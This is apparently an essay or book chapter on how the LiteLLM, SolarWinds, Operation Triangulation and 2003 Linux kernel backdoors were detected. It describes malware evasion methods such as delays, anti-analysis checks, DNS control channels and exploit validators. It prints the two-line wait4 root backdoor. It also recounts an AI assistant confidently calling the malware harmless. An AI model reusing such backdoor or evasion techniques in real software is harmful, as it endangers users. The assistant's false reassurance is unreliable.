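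On 24 March the attackers uploaded two malicious versions of LiteLLM, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8. Both collected passwords, SSH keys and cloud credentials, encrypted them and sent them to a web address that resembled LiteLLM's own. In 1.82.7 the attackers put the malware in one of LiteLLM's own files, and ITPro's *LiteLLM PyPI compromise* explains that it ran when a program imported that file. Version 1.82.8 also contained a file called litellm_init.pth. Python executes certain lines in .pth files whenever it starts, so the malware in this version ran even if no program used LiteLLM.

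The line in litellm_init.pth started a second copy of Python to run the malware. The second copy read the same file as it started, so it launched a third, and so on. The malware also started another Python process to collect the credentials, which triggered the file again. Since each copy of the malware could start more than one new process, the number of processes grew exponentially, which programmers call a fork bomb. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) describes this as a bug in the malware. The attackers could have prevented it by setting a marker when the malware started and checking for it before each new launch.

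### From a frozen laptop to a public warning

Callum McMahon, an engineer at FutureSearch, installed the new version unintentionally when his code editor, Cursor, started a small helper program that depended on LiteLLM and the installer fetched the latest release. His laptop, a Mac with 48 GB of memory, slowed until he had to force it to shut down. The times below come mainly from FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* (2026), which includes the record of his investigation. The first upload time is from LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), and the quarantine time is derived from PyPI's figures.

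| Time (UTC) | Minutes from upload of 1.82.8 | Event |
|---|---|---|
| 10:39 | −13 | Attackers upload 1.82.7 |
| 10:52 | 0 | Attackers upload 1.82.8 |
| 10:58 | 6 | McMahon's editor downloads it |
| 11:07 | 15 | The malware starts installing a permanent copy of itself |
| 11:09 | 17 | McMahon forces the laptop off, with about 11,000 processes running |
| 11:13 | 21 | He begins to investigate with an AI assistant |
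| 11:40 | 48 | They find the malicious file |
| 11:58 | 66 | He confirms that PyPI is still distributing it and emails PyPI |
| 12:04 | 72 | He shares a public warning |
| 12:30 | 98 | FutureSearch adds 1.82.7 to its warning |
| 13:11 | 139 | PyPI quarantines the package |

PyPI reported that the exposure lasted 2 hours and 32 minutes, which fits the other evidence. LiteLLM's own figure of about 40 minutes from 10:39 can't be right, because McMahon downloaded a fresh copy from PyPI at 11:58.

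McMahon had photographed the list of processes before turning the laptop off. Each entry was a Python command followed by text in base64, which encodes any data as letters, digits and a few symbols. He asked Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, what had happened. It first answered that the pattern was "not malware", because programming tools, including Claude Code itself, often pass code to Python this way. It attributed the problem to a runaway loop in one of its own sessions, and later to an update to Cursor.

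McMahon kept asking, and typed in the start of the encoded text from his photograph. A search of the installed tools found the same text in litellm_init.pth. He needed the photograph because forcing the laptop off had prevented the system from recording any diagnostic information about the crash. He then had Claude download the package into an isolated container and inspect the file without running it, which confirmed that the malware came from PyPI.

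Claude saved McMahon time by searching logs and package caches, decoding the malware, explaining each stage and supplying the address for reporting it. He argues that developers without security training can now raise an alarm much faster. But Claude also confidently gave him several innocent explanations, any of which a less persistent person might have accepted. McMahon said it took some scepticism to make Claude look for malice.

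LiteLLM's GitHub repository gave further evidence. The developers normally marked each release there, but the latest one marked was a form of 1.82.6, which suggested that someone had uploaded the new versions directly to PyPI. Anyone could have noticed the missing release from 10:39 onwards, but McMahon checked for it only after he had found the malware. Checking the installed files against the package's own manifest would have revealed nothing, because the manifest listed litellm_init.pth and its cryptographic fingerprint.

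### Would better code have stayed hidden?

Neither crash helped the attackers. McMahon's hurt them directly, because his forced restart interrupted the malware while it was installing its permanent copy and left an empty file. The malware in 1.82.8 would not have frozen his laptop if it had a working check against relaunching. We don't know what change would have fixed Stuxnet, but a version that did not crash Windows was evidently possible. Stuxnet had spread for about a year before Ulasen's case, so most infected computers presumably kept working.

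Several commentators concluded that, without the crashes, the LiteLLM malware would have gone unnoticed for a long time. InfoQ's *PyPI Supply Chain Attack Compromises LiteLLM, Enabling the Exfiltration of Sensitive Information* attributes this view to the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy. LM Market Cap's *LiteLLM Supply Chain Attack* suggests that the malware would have stayed hidden for "days or weeks". Trend Micro's *Your AI Stack Just Handed Over Your Root Keys* (2026) claims that the attackers would still have been stealing secrets when it was written.

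Version 1.82.7 slightly supports this view. It carried malware without the faulty start-up file, and PyPI received no report about either version until McMahon's, 79 minutes after 1.82.7 appeared. But 79 minutes is a short time, and security researchers were already following the attackers, whose campaign, according to Datadog, had passed through Trivy, the JavaScript package system npm and the security company Checkmarx. Boost Security's *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* (2026) describes how the researcher Rami McCarthy identified LiteLLM as a target from a clue about a project with more than 35,000 stars on GitHub. He might have found the malware without any crash, though it is hard to say how much later.

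A second attack on LiteLLM is a better test. On 21 October 2026 somebody published version 1.107.0 with malware that also ran whenever Python started. This malware had the safeguard that was missing from the first attack. ITmedia's *Pythonを起動するだけで認証情報が盗まれる LiteLLMに混入した悪性コードの正体* (2026) describes an environment variable that stopped it from running twice and a marker file that stopped it from collecting the same data again. It was also harder to spot from the release records. LiteLLM (2026) acknowledged that its own release system had built, signed and published the package, and GitHub had a matching release. Only comparing the package's contents with the source would have revealed three extra files.

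Even so, several security companies noticed the attack within six minutes, according to TecnoAndroid's *LiteLLM compromesso* (2026). Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026) reported that the package stayed on PyPI for about an hour and three quarters. Although it was better written than the faulty March version, it lasted some 50 minutes less.

This is strong but not conclusive evidence against "days or weeks" for a package as popular as LiteLLM. The March attack had given security companies a reason to watch LiteLLM closely, and they might have been slower the first time or with an obscure package. The intrusion behind the October release also lasted much longer than the release itself. The Vanguard USA's *How one unrevoked key let attackers poison LiteLLM* (2026) reports that the attacker gained owner-level access to LiteLLM's repositories on 10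 October, and apparently nobody noticed for eleven days.

PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the malicious March versions in 152 minutes, or nearly 800 a minute. At that rate, another day would have added over a million downloads. The March attack still did serious harm despite its early discovery. The security company Hudson Rock later linked the stolen data to 2,488 corporate domains. In October, the attacker was testing stolen cloud credentials about four and a half hours after taking them.

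"Days or weeks" would be far too short for Stuxnet, which went undetected for about a year even with the fault that caused the crashes. Without the crashes, it might have lasted much longer. No security company was inspecting the software on Iranian engineers' flash drives within minutes of its release, and the one engineer known to have suspected a virus there had scanned for it and found nothing.

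## How was the SolarWinds implant traced from one phone registration?

FireEye found the implant in SolarWinds' Orion in December 2020 because the intruders also had to log in to FireEye's network, and one of them left an odd record when logging in. Stuxnet and the LiteLLM malware were discovered because their code malfunctioned on victims' machines, but no crash or slowdown led anyone to the Orion implant. NYU's *SEC Charges SolarWinds and Its CISO with Fraud and Internal Controls Failures* reports that the US government attributed the operation to Russia's foreign intelligence service in April 2021.

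### The second phone

FireEye used two-factor authentication, so employees needed both a password and a code from their phone to get into the network. An intruder with a stolen password could get the code by registering another phone on the employee's account. In late November, someone registered a new phone on an employee's account, which triggered an alert. Zetter's *Sun Stroke* calls it a routine alert that many others would have ignored. An analyst followed it up, and FireEye established that the employee had not registered the phone.

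This check took very little effort and gave almost conclusive evidence of an intrusion. Odd traffic may have dozens of harmless causes, but it is hard to think of an innocent reason for a stranger's phone to be registered on an employee's account. However, nothing in the alert connected the intrusion to SolarWinds.

By this stage the intruders hardly needed the implant, because they could log in as FireEye employees. Mandia described their methods at a February 2021 hearing, recorded in the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence's *Open Hearing* (2022). They came in through the implant and immediately took the keys and tokens that FireEye's systems used to recognise its staff. With these they could read email and documents, and steal the tools that FireEye used to imitate attackers when testing its clients' security.

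The intruders might have avoided the alert. At the think tank that Volexity investigated, the same group had gone after a secret key that connected the mail server to its two-factor service. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, explains that this key let the intruders calculate the login codes themselves. Someone with those codes doesn't need to register a phone, and it isn't clear why the intruders registered one at FireEye.

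### A server with nothing wrong on it

About 100 people worked on FireEye's investigation. They searched thousands of computers for the earliest trace of the intruders to learn how the break-in had started. FireEye announced the breach on 8 December, when it still didn't know how the intruders had first got in.

The earliest trace Mandia's staff could find was on a server that ran SolarWinds software. Mandia told NPR, in an interview that GBH published, that they examined the server and could find nothing bad on it.

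The intruders took care to leave few traces. FireEye reported that they would replace a legitimate utility with their own program, run it, and then restore the original, and that they did the same with scheduled tasks. Once they had ordinary remote access, they routinely deleted their tools, including backdoors. They connected from internet addresses in the victim's country. FireEye knew of no other incident involving the addresses used against it, so a list of suspicious addresses from another victim would not have helped.

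The trail began at the server, but this was fairly weak evidence that Orion contained an implant. The intruders could have entered the server with a stolen password or through an accidental vulnerability, or they could have left earlier traces elsewhere that FireEye had missed. Mandia told the Senate that the software was "the last place you'd look", but FireEye had exhausted its other leads and employed people who could take the software apart.

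FireEye decided to decompile the entire SolarWinds platform to find out whether it contained an implant. Mandia told NPR that the material came to 14 gigabytes and over 18,000 files. He told the Senate that there were 3,500 executable files and over a million lines of assembly, a readable form of machine instructions, but elsewhere he mentioned 4,000 executable files and millions of lines. These are round numbers from memory, and neither the interview nor the testimony makes clear how much of the code people read and how much they searched with programs.

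The implant was in a single plug-in, a file that adds functions to a larger program. The search seems to have taken at most four days, since Mandia places it after the 8 December announcement and FireEye informed SolarWinds on 12 December. FireEye published technical details the next day so that other organisations could check their systems.

### Inside the build

The US Securities and Exchange Commission alleged in a complaint against SolarWinds (SEC (2023)) that the attackers entered the company's network in January 2019 through its remote access system. In October 2019 they put harmless code into an Orion update to check that their changes would reach customers. They probably built Sunspot, CrowdStrike's name for the tool that inserted the implant, on 20 February 2020. SolarWinds signed the infected plug-in on 24 March, and three versions of Orion released between March and June contained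 the implant. WHYY's *A ‘worst nightmare’ cyberattack* quotes an update notice: "This release includes bug fixes, increased stability and performance improvements."

Sunspot's brief swap of one source file during each build left the repository clean. The attackers took great care that this would not cause a build error, because SolarWinds' programmers would have looked for the cause. CrowdStrike describes several precautions:

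- Sunspot calculated a cryptographic fingerprint of the original file and left the file alone if the fingerprint was not the one it expected. A legitimate edit to that file would therefore have stopped the attack until the attackers updated their tool.
- It checked the malicious replacement in the same way, in case decryption had failed and produced garbage.
- The replacement contained instructions that turned off compiler warnings around the added code, which kept those warnings out of the build logs.
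- The attackers could signal Sunspot to finish its current work and exit. Killing it partway through might have left a half-altered source file behind.

They were just as careful about errors in Orion itself. The lines they added first checked whether the implant was already running, then started it in the background and silently discarded any error that occurred while starting it. The March version of the LiteLLM malware had no working check for whether it was already running, which is why it froze McMahon's laptop.

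CrowdStrike compared the source code that Sunspot inserted with what a decompiler produces from the finished plug-in and found the two nearly identical. The attackers had compressed and encoded the revealing text and given the main part of the implant a name that resembled the Orion Improvement Program, a genuine SolarWinds service. An analyst who opened the plug-in could still have followed most of the code, but would first have had to know which of several thousand files to open.

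### Two weeks of waiting

FireEye named the implant Sunburst. When Orion loaded Sunburst, the implant first checked that it was running inside the expected Orion program. It then waited until its file was 12 to 14 days old, with the threshold chosen at random. It stopped if the computer did not belong to a Windows domain, the kind of managed network that most large organisations have.

The implant next checked the computer's programs, services and drivers against lists of security and analysis tools. If it found a listed program or driver, it stopped and tried again later. If it found a listed service, it disabled it by changing a Windows setting before trying again later. The lists contained only hashes, which are numbers calculated from the tools' names, so analysts had to guess names and check whether their hashes matched. The xz implant hid function names in a similar way.

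Because of these checks, someone who installed the update in a laboratory and watched it for a week would have seen nothing. A longer test would also have failed if the computer was outside a domain or was running a listed analysis program. The delay also made an administrator who noticed strange traffic less likely to connect it with an update from two weeks before.

Sunburst first contacted its operators through DNS, the system computers use to look up the numerical address for a name. The implant made up a long name under a domain the attackers controlled, avsvmcloud. The first part of the name contained an identifier for the machine and an encoded form of the organisation's domain name. The middle looked like the name of an ordinary Amazon cloud service. DNS passes a query along until it reaches the server responsible for the domain, so the attackers could learn from the lookup alone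 whom they had infected, without the victim's computer connecting to theirs.

The attackers used the reply to control the implant. An address in certain ranges made the implant shut down permanently, while a reply that pointed to a second name directed it to a server for commands. The implant waited for irregular periods between queries, normally from a minute to two hours, and up to nine hours after an error.

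The implant's later traffic imitated that of the Orion Improvement Program. Its commands arrived in what looked like a harmless data file, split into fragments across many strings of digits and letters. The implant also mixed random entries into the data it sent back. Someone reading the traffic would have needed to know the decoding method to see anything wrong with its content.

Most victims never had this later traffic. According to the SEC, nearly 18,000 customers received the infected software, and the attackers later attacked about 100 of them. The others would have seen almost no sign except some DNS queries. Some may not have had even those, because the backdoor worked only if Orion could reach the internet. Ramakrishna (2021), in *Written Testimony of Sudhakar Ramakrishna*, notes that Orion does not need internet access. A customer who had blocked that access would have been safe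 without knowing about the implant.

DNS logs recorded the queries for months before anyone understood them. Unit 42 later searched the logs of Palo Alto Networks' DNS security service and found requests for the attackers' domain from April to November 2020, peaking in July. Those logs could show many organisations contacting the same unusual domain, but a domain that many organisations contact may well belong to a legitimate product.

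Once FireEye understood the replies, it worked with Microsoft and the domain registrar GoDaddy to make the domain return a reply that shut the implant down. This did not remove intruders who had already moved to other parts of a network.

### Three earlier sightings

In late May 2020, more than six months before FireEye's discovery, the US Justice Department noticed that a server running a trial version of Orion was communicating with an unfamiliar system on the internet. Schneier on Security's *SolarWinds Detected Six Months Earlier* quotes Wired's report that the department asked Mandiant, which FireEye already owned, to find out whether someone had hacked the server, and that it also brought in Microsoft.

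The investigators suspected that the hackers had broken into the server directly, possibly through a vulnerability in Orion. beSpacific's *The Untold Story of the Boldest Supply-Chain Hack Ever*, an excerpt from a Wired article, says that the department contacted SolarWinds and named a file that might be involved. SolarWinds' engineers could not find a vulnerability in their code, and after weeks of correspondence the two sides stopped communicating without solving the mystery.

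The engineers' answer may have been accurate, because the attackers had not needed a vulnerability in Orion to get onto the server. The malicious code was also not in the engineers' repository, so reading the source code there would not have revealed it.

Volexity's investigation of the think tank's SolarWinds server also stalled that summer. The Justice Department did not know about Volexity's case, which Wired calls "uncannily similar" to the department's.

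Palo Alto Networks had the clearest evidence. Its Orion server queried the attackers' domain on 29 September. On 5 October the server downloaded Cobalt Strike Beacon, a commercial remote-control tool that intruders often misuse. The company's security software recognised the behaviour and blocked the program before it could run. Staff isolated the server, checked the rest of the network and notified SolarWinds. The company's Unit 42 writes that staff thought the incident was isolated.

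The SEC's complaint gives one side's allegations about how SolarWinds handled these reports. It refers to the customers only as a government agency and a cybersecurity firm, but Holland & Knight's *Court in SolarWinds Case Blows Down SEC's Cyber Enforcement Authority* (2024) names them as the Justice Department's US Trustee Program and Palo Alto Networks. A judge dismissed most of the case in July 2024 (Downes, Friedlander and Prager, *Court Dismisses Most of SEC's Claims Against SolarWinds*, 2024). At that stage a court assumes that the alleged facts are true and decides whether they would break the law, so the ruling did not settle what SolarWinds' staff had said or known.

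According to the complaint, the agency reported in June that Orion was trying to contact unknown websites, which "spooked" one SolarWinds engineer. Brown, the head of information security, thought an attacker was either already on the customer's system or studying Orion for use in larger attacks. Neither quite meant that SolarWinds itself had shipped the malicious code. The company's investigation then uncovered numerous vulnerabilities in Orion, more than its engineers could keep up with. With so many ordinary faults, an implant was not the obvious explanation. Jia Tan had benefited similarly from a genuine bug in xz.

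SolarWinds' security staff noticed in October that Palo Alto Networks' report resembled the agency's. In both cases, a part of Orion called the Business Layer Host had downloaded malicious files. On a call on 5 November, Palo Alto Networks asked whether SolarWinds had seen Orion behave like this before. A SolarWinds employee said it had not, and messaged a colleague, "Well I just lied." Palo Alto Networks later replied that an unknown vulnerability seemed to be responsible and urged SolarWinds to treat the case as an outside attack. If this account is right, Palo Alto Networks believed its incident was isolated partly because SolarWinds had concealed the other one.

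The Business Layer Host was a strong clue because it loaded the infected plug-in. By October, SolarWinds had two independent reports about this component, and searching the files it loads would have been a much smaller task than FireEye's search. Comparing the release with a rebuild from clean source should also have exposed the implant. Ramakrishna, who became chief executive after the discovery, told the Senate that SolarWinds was adding checks that its compiled releases match their source.

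FireEye shared the decompiled code with Brown and others on 12 December. Brown had connected the code with both earlier reports by the following day at the latest, and he later testified that this took no further analysis. In January 2021 SolarWinds said publicly that it believed the incidents in those reports were related to the attack.

### Why FireEye found it

FireEye's alert, a phone registration, had no visible connection with Orion. The Justice Department and Palo Alto Networks had better alerts. The department had seen Orion itself making strange connections, and Palo Alto Networks had caught an Orion server downloading malware. All four investigations got as far as a SolarWinds server, but only FireEye suspected that the signed software on it might be malicious and took all of it apart. The Justice Department's investigators asked the vendor to look for a fault, and Palo Alto Networks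 closed its case after its defences had apparently worked.

Skill was necessary, but it can't be the whole explanation, since Mandiant and Microsoft had both been involved in the Justice Department's case. FireEye had much more reason to persist in December. Intruders had stolen its tools, it had publicly announced the theft, and it still did not know how they had got in. A client with one suspicious trial server can disconnect it and move on. Palo Alto Networks had blocked the payload, which probably also made finding out how it had arrived seem less urgent.

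Mandia told the Senate that nearly everyone who worked on FireEye's investigation was highly experienced. Few companies could spare such people to investigate every unexplained connection, especially when most turn out to be harmless.

At the same hearing, Senator Marco Rubio suggested that the operation might still have been running if FireEye had not investigated its alert. This is plausible, even though three organisations had noticed something wrong within about five months and SolarWinds' own staff had linked two of the cases. When FireEye called about two months after the staff made that link, they still had not found the implant.

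## How was spyware found on iPhones that could not be inspected?

FireEye could analyze Orion because it had a copy of every file. In early 2023 the security company Kaspersky began to suspect that someone had hacked its employees' iPhones. It had the phones but could not read the software running on them. The first evidence came from the company's network. Kaspersky's researchers then took months to recover the code by intercepting it on its way to the phones. They named the campaign Operation Triangulation.

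The attackers sent this implant to chosen people rather than hiding it in a product or an update. They used exploits, which are pieces of code that take advantage of a vulnerability. Four of the vulnerabilities were zero-days, meaning Apple did not yet know about them and had no fix.

### A pattern in the office Wi-Fi

Kaspersky ran a separate Wi-Fi network for mobile devices and watched it with KUMA, a monitoring system that it also sells. Kaspersky (2023) reported that this system showed suspicious activity from several iPhones. When analysts in the Moscow headquarters looked more closely at the traffic, they found the same sequence each time:

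1. The phone contacted Apple's iMessage servers and downloaded something that could have been an attachment.
2. It exchanged data with a server called backuprabbit for less than a minute.
3. It held a longer session with one of five other servers, which had names like cloudsponcer and unlimitedteacup.
4. When the phone restarted, all of this stopped.

Each step looks ordinary on its own, because phones contact iMessage all day and connect to unfamiliar servers whenever someone opens a web page. Kaspersky began collecting the phones once its analysts recognised a clear pattern.

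The connections used HTTPS, which encrypts the content of web traffic, so the analysts could not read what the phones had sent. A network can still record which servers a phone contacts, when, and how much data passes each way. Like someone who sees only a neural network's outputs, the analysts could describe what the phones did but not the code that caused it.

The owners could see even less, because the malicious message was malformed in a way that produced no notification, and the malware deleted it afterwards. The malware could also block iOS updates, so some owners might have seen an update fail with an error message, but that is easy to blame on a poor connection. The spyware's full control of the phone let it erase records there but not in Kaspersky's network logs, and any data it sent over the office Wi-Fi had to pass through Kaspersky's equipment.

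### What the backups contained

Apple's restrictions prevent an iPhone's owner from copying everything on it. Forensic programs use exploits to get around these restrictions, but the ones available at the time did not work on modern iPhone processors running iOS 15 or 16, so the investigators lacked the access that the attackers had.

The team turned to iTunes backups, which contain part of a phone's file system and some of its databases. They assumed that the attackers were reading their messages and listening through the phones' microphones, so they met in person, with the phones in airplane mode and sometimes in bags that block radio signals. They later found that the spyware did include a module for recording sound.

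They processed the backups with the Mobile Verification Toolkit, a free program that sorts the timestamps of files and database records into a single timeline. They first looked for a malicious attachment in the iMessage folders, where Citizen Lab had found the FORCEDENTRY exploit in 2021. They found no exploit or malware.

The investigators knew from network records when each phone had made its suspicious connections, so they looked for events that recurred in the timelines around those times. They found that a program called BackupAgent was using the network, although Apple had retired it years before and it should not have been running.

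In Kaspersky's published example, from 13 September 2022, the program that downloads iMessage attachments was active at 10:04:11. An attachment folder changed at 10:04:54 but was left empty, which suggests that something had deleted a file. BackupAgent appeared at 10:05:14. The record lists about 730 kilobytes received and 290 kilobytes sent over the mobile network, so monitoring the office Wi-Fi could not have captured that traffic.

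Kaspersky considered BackupAgent the most reliable sign of infection and released a free tool that checks backups for such traces. (BackupAgent2 is a legitimate program, so a careless search would produce false positives.) The team could now tell which phones were infected, but it still had none of the malicious code.

### How the attack worked

The researchers eventually recovered the whole chain of exploits. According to Larin, Bezvershenko and Kucherin (2023), who worked on the investigation, it began with an attachment that the phone processed without showing anything to its owner. The attachment ran code by exploiting a flaw in an obscure font instruction dating from the early 1990s. That code included a JavaScript program of about 11,000 lines, which used a kernel flaw to read and write all of the phone's memory.

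Newer iPhones have hardware that protects the most sensitive parts of kernel memory. The attackers bypassed it by writing to hardware registers, small storage locations in the chip, that Apple's own firmware did not use. They could then have installed spyware immediately, but their code instead erased traces of the attack and invisibly opened Safari on a page hosted at backuprabbit.

A script on that page, which Kaspersky calls the JavaScript validator, collected information about the browser. It also drew a yellow triangle, which gave the campaign its name, and calculated a checksum from the pixels. Different devices draw the same shape slightly differently, so the checksum helped identify the hardware and software. If the attackers' server accepted the results, it sent an exploit for a flaw in Safari, the fourth zero-day, followed by another exploit for the kernel.

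These loaded a second validator, this time a compiled program. Kaspersky found that it listed the running processes and installed apps, deleted crash logs, and searched several databases for traces of the malicious message. It also checked whether the phone was jailbroken, meaning that Apple's restrictions had been removed, as is common on phones that researchers use for experiments. The server sent the implant only after this check.

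The validators were there to keep the exploits and the implant away from security researchers, but the attackers had chosen a security company's employees as victims. Kaspersky's researchers did not need to make a laboratory phone look like a victim's, because their colleagues' phones were real targets.

Kaspersky named the implant TriangleDB. It had 24 commands, including ones to copy files, steal saved passwords, track the phone's location and load further modules. It ran only in memory, so even a perfect copy of the phone's storage would not have contained it. It disappeared when the phone restarted. Without a restart, it removed itself after 30 days unless the attackers extended that period.

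This made TriangleDB hard to find on a phone. But the attackers had to repeat the whole infection after every restart, so investigators had repeated chances to observe it, as they did with the xz backdoor.

### Catching the code in transit

The team first tried to capture the message by setting up a Mac with a script that recorded incoming iMessages. Several targeted colleagues logged in to it with their Apple accounts. The attackers soon reinfected one of the phones, but the Mac recorded no message, and Kaspersky never found out why.

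The team then took phones that the attackers had previously infected and routed all their internet traffic through its own server. A phone normally accepts an HTTPS connection only if an authority it trusts has vouched for the server at the other end, so the team installed its own certificate on the phones to make them trust its server. A program on the server called mitmproxy could then decrypt the traffic, record it and pass it on. Apple's own services mostly rejected the team's certificate because they accept only particular ones, so iMessage remained unreadable.

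At the next infection the proxy captured the JavaScript validator, but the validator encrypted its messages a second time, with a private key that it generated at random and never sent. The team wrote a mitmproxy add-on that edited the script as it passed through, making it use a key they had supplied, rather than trying to break the encryption. After another infection they could read the messages and extract the Safari exploit, the kernel exploit and the second validator.

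The second validator's instructions for hiding the attack included a database search for .watchface attachments, a format for Apple Watch faces. From this, the researchers learned what kind of file they were looking for.

The team needed both the iMessage attachment and the key to decrypt it. iMessage encrypts each attachment with a random key, uploads the encrypted file to Apple's iCloud storage, and sends the recipient a link and the key. Apple's strict certificate rules did not apply to links to iCloud attachments, so the proxy could capture the encrypted file. But the proxy couldn't read the key, which was sent through iMessage, and the malware deleted the evidence after a successful infection. The team therefore changed a few bytes of the file in transit. The download failed and the exploit did not run, so the key stayed in the phone's message database. The team backed up the phone,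 extracted the key and decrypted the attachment.

To get the implant, the researchers used the proxy to overwrite one instruction in the second validator, the call to its encryption function, with an instruction that does nothing. The validator then sent its data to the proxy unencrypted. The proxy encrypted the data with a key the researchers controlled and forwarded it to the attackers' server, which used the same key to encrypt its reply. That reply contained TriangleDB. The researchers later replaced an encryption key inside TriangleDB itself to obtain its modules. Their addition to mitmproxy had grown from 30 lines of code to about 400.

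All of this depended on the attackers continuing to send code to the phones. Researchers had found the FORCEDENTRY exploit in backups, but they could not recover its payload because the server that supplied it was no longer accessible when they analysed the exploit.

### Five months, after at least three years

Kaspersky says it took "about half a year" to collect the chain. It must have had the implant slightly sooner, because it was already analysing the final payload when it published its first public report on 1 June 2023, about five months after an alert at the beginning of the year. Malpedia, a malware catalogue, dates Kaspersky's full description of TriangleDB to 21 June.

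Callum McMahon found the LiteLLM malware 27 minutes after he began investigating, on a laptop where he could open any file. Comparing this with Kaspersky's investigation exaggerates the effect of Apple's restrictions, since the LiteLLM attackers were much less careful. But many of Kaspersky's steps would have been unnecessary on a computer whose memory the researchers could read, because the implant and the keys were in memory while it ran.

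Kaspersky found traces of infection dating back to 2019, so the campaign had operated for at least three years before the alert. The researchers could see this far back because a new iPhone set up from an old one keeps the old phone's records, including the original timestamps. The campaign may have started earlier, since some modules contained code for versions of iOS older than 8.0, which people mostly used before 2015, but attackers can reuse old code in a new campaign.

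Network monitoring therefore did not catch Triangulation early. The phones may have been infected on the Wi-Fi without anyone noticing, or while they were elsewhere. People who don't work for an organisation that monitors its network would have had even less chance of noticing an infection. Kaspersky's *Connecting the Dots* (2023) reports that the company was not the only target and that other victims confirmed infections after Kaspersky released its tool.

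Russia's security service, the FSB, claimed that US intelligence was responsible and had Apple's help. Computer Weekly notes that nobody has verified this and quotes Apple's denial that it has ever helped a government build a backdoor. Kaspersky did not name an attacker. Most of what we know about the investigation comes from Kaspersky, which was a victim and also sells the system that raised the alert. However, Apple's patches for the vulnerabilities are good independent evidence that the exploits were real.

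### Does a closed system protect its user?

In *A matter of triangulation* (2023), Eugene Kaspersky, who heads the company, blamed the closed design of iOS. He called it a "black box" in which spyware can hide for years, and argued that a lack of news about attacks does not mean there are none. The investigation supports both points, since the attackers had full control of the phones while the owners and a team of experts had to work from partial backups.

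According to Kaspersky's first technical report, the spyware probably could not survive a restart because of the limits iOS imposes. The restrictions that made the phones hard to inspect therefore also seem to have forced the attackers to keep reinfecting them, which created the traffic that led to their discovery. A more open phone would have been easier to inspect, but it might also have let the spyware install itself permanently and avoid creating that traffic.

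Access to Apple's software would not have revealed everything either. Larin searched the publicly available source code, the kernel and various firmware files for references to the hardware registers that the attackers had used to bypass the memory protection, and found none. It is still unknown how the attackers learned about these registers.

### The same exploit in 2026

The code that Kaspersky recovered proved useful again three years later, in March 2026, when Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Coruna* (2026) described a kit of 23 iPhone exploits that worked on iOS versions 13.0 to 17.2.1. According to Help Net Security's *Coruna* (2026), Google's researchers first saw a surveillance company's customer using the kit in February 2025. In July a suspected Russian espionage group was using it on Ukrainian websites, and by December criminals were using it on fake Chinese gambling and cryptocurrency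 sites to steal from digital wallets. Roshan and Stein (2026), in *MoldyRoost*, found online advertisements spreading exploit kits from the Coruna family as late as November 2026.

Coruna exploited two of the same vulnerabilities as Triangulation. This was weak evidence of a connection, because details of the vulnerabilities had been public for years and other people had written their own exploits. Kaspersky's Boris Larin said in a company press release (2026) that "shared vulnerabilities alone don't prove shared authorship."

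Some of the kit's download links still worked, so Kaspersky collected and decrypted its components. Kaspersky's *Coruna* concludes that one of the five kernel exploits is an updated version of the one from Triangulation. The other four use the same framework, and two of them were written after Kaspersky exposed Triangulation.

The updated exploit checks for iOS 17.2 and for processors released in late 2023, even though Apple had fixed the vulnerabilities the exploit needs in a test version of iOS 16.5. These checks would be pointless in a standalone exploit. According to Kaspersky, the developers built all five exploits from shared source code, so checks they added for newer exploits also appeared in the old one when they recompiled it.

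Kaspersky says in its press release that it is confident the same author created the kernel exploits in both campaigns. In its technical article, it is more cautious about the kit as a whole, and assumes only that it is an updated version of a framework used "at least to some extent" in Triangulation. Neither claim identifies who ran Triangulation, since Coruna passed between several unrelated groups. Kaspersky could compare the exploits only because it had extracted the original in 2023. The Wi-Fi records that raised the alert would not have shown that two exploits shared code.

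## What have integrity checks and code review caught?

In November 2003, somebody added a backdoor to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code. An automatic file comparison exposed it within a day, without anyone having reported a crash or a slow login. Nobody had recognised the malicious lines by reading the code until the comparison showed where to look.

The kernel's developers then kept their main repository in BitKeeper, a commercial system from Larry McVoy's company, BitMover. Some developers did not want to use BitKeeper, so BitMover maintained a public copy of the source in CVS, an older system. Changes passed only from the main repository to the copy. The conversion program added a note to the copy's log linking each change to the original in BitKeeper.

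McVoy (2003) explained the procedure to the kernel mailing list in *BK2CVS problem*. BitMover converted the repository on an internal machine, copied the updated files to the public server, then compared checksums of the two sets of files. A checksum is a short number calculated from a file's contents, and almost any change to the file changes the number. The comparison ran every night and sent an email if anything differed. On 5 November it flagged the file exit.c.

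McVoy found three changes in the file's log that had no link to BitKeeper. All three were dated the day before and carried the name of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer. The first added two lines. The other two removed 58 lines and put them back, with a comment apologising for editing the wrong file. Miller said he had not made the changes, and McVoy concluded that someone had altered the public copy directly.

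Later accounts in Freedom to Tinker, a technology policy blog, and InfoQ's *A Look Back at the Linux Kernel Backdoor* say the missing links exposed the change. But in McVoy's own account, the checksums raised the alert and the missing links helped him trace it.

### Two lines that looked like an error check

McVoy's first message treated the matter as a nuisance. He had already repaired the file, and he wrote that it was "not a big deal". Thirteen minutes later another developer, Matthew Dharm, asked out of curiosity what the changed lines were. McVoy posted them:

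```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Within ten minutes, Zwane Mwaikambo replied that the code looked odd. Fifteen minutes later, Chad Kitching asked whether it was an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy praised the catch and said he had missed it.

The lines belong to wait4, a function that a program calls to wait for another program it has started. They appear to return an error for an invalid combination of options. But in C, the language of the kernel, `==` compares two values and `=` stores one. `current->uid` is the ID of the user running the program, and ID 0 belongs to root, the administrator, who can do anything on the machine. The code therefore makes the user root instead of checking whether the user is root.

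Two rules of C kept this from causing visible trouble. The computer evaluates the part after `&&` only if the part before it is true, so an ordinary call to wait4 leaves the user ID alone. An assignment also has the value it stored, here 0, which C treats as false, so the condition fails and the error line never runs. The program carries on with root's powers. The strange combination of options is the trigger, and an attacker would already have needed a way to run a program on the machine.

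The gcc compiler can warn about an assignment used as a condition, but Tomas Szepe pointed out on the mailing list that the extra parentheses around this one prevent the warning.

The people who recognised the backdoor had a great advantage over an ordinary reviewer, because they were looking at two lines out of millions and knew that an unknown person had put them there without permission. McVoy knew this too and still missed the backdoor. Another developer, Andreas Dilger, thought a change like this might have taken "a good while to find" if it had slipped into the kernel without review.

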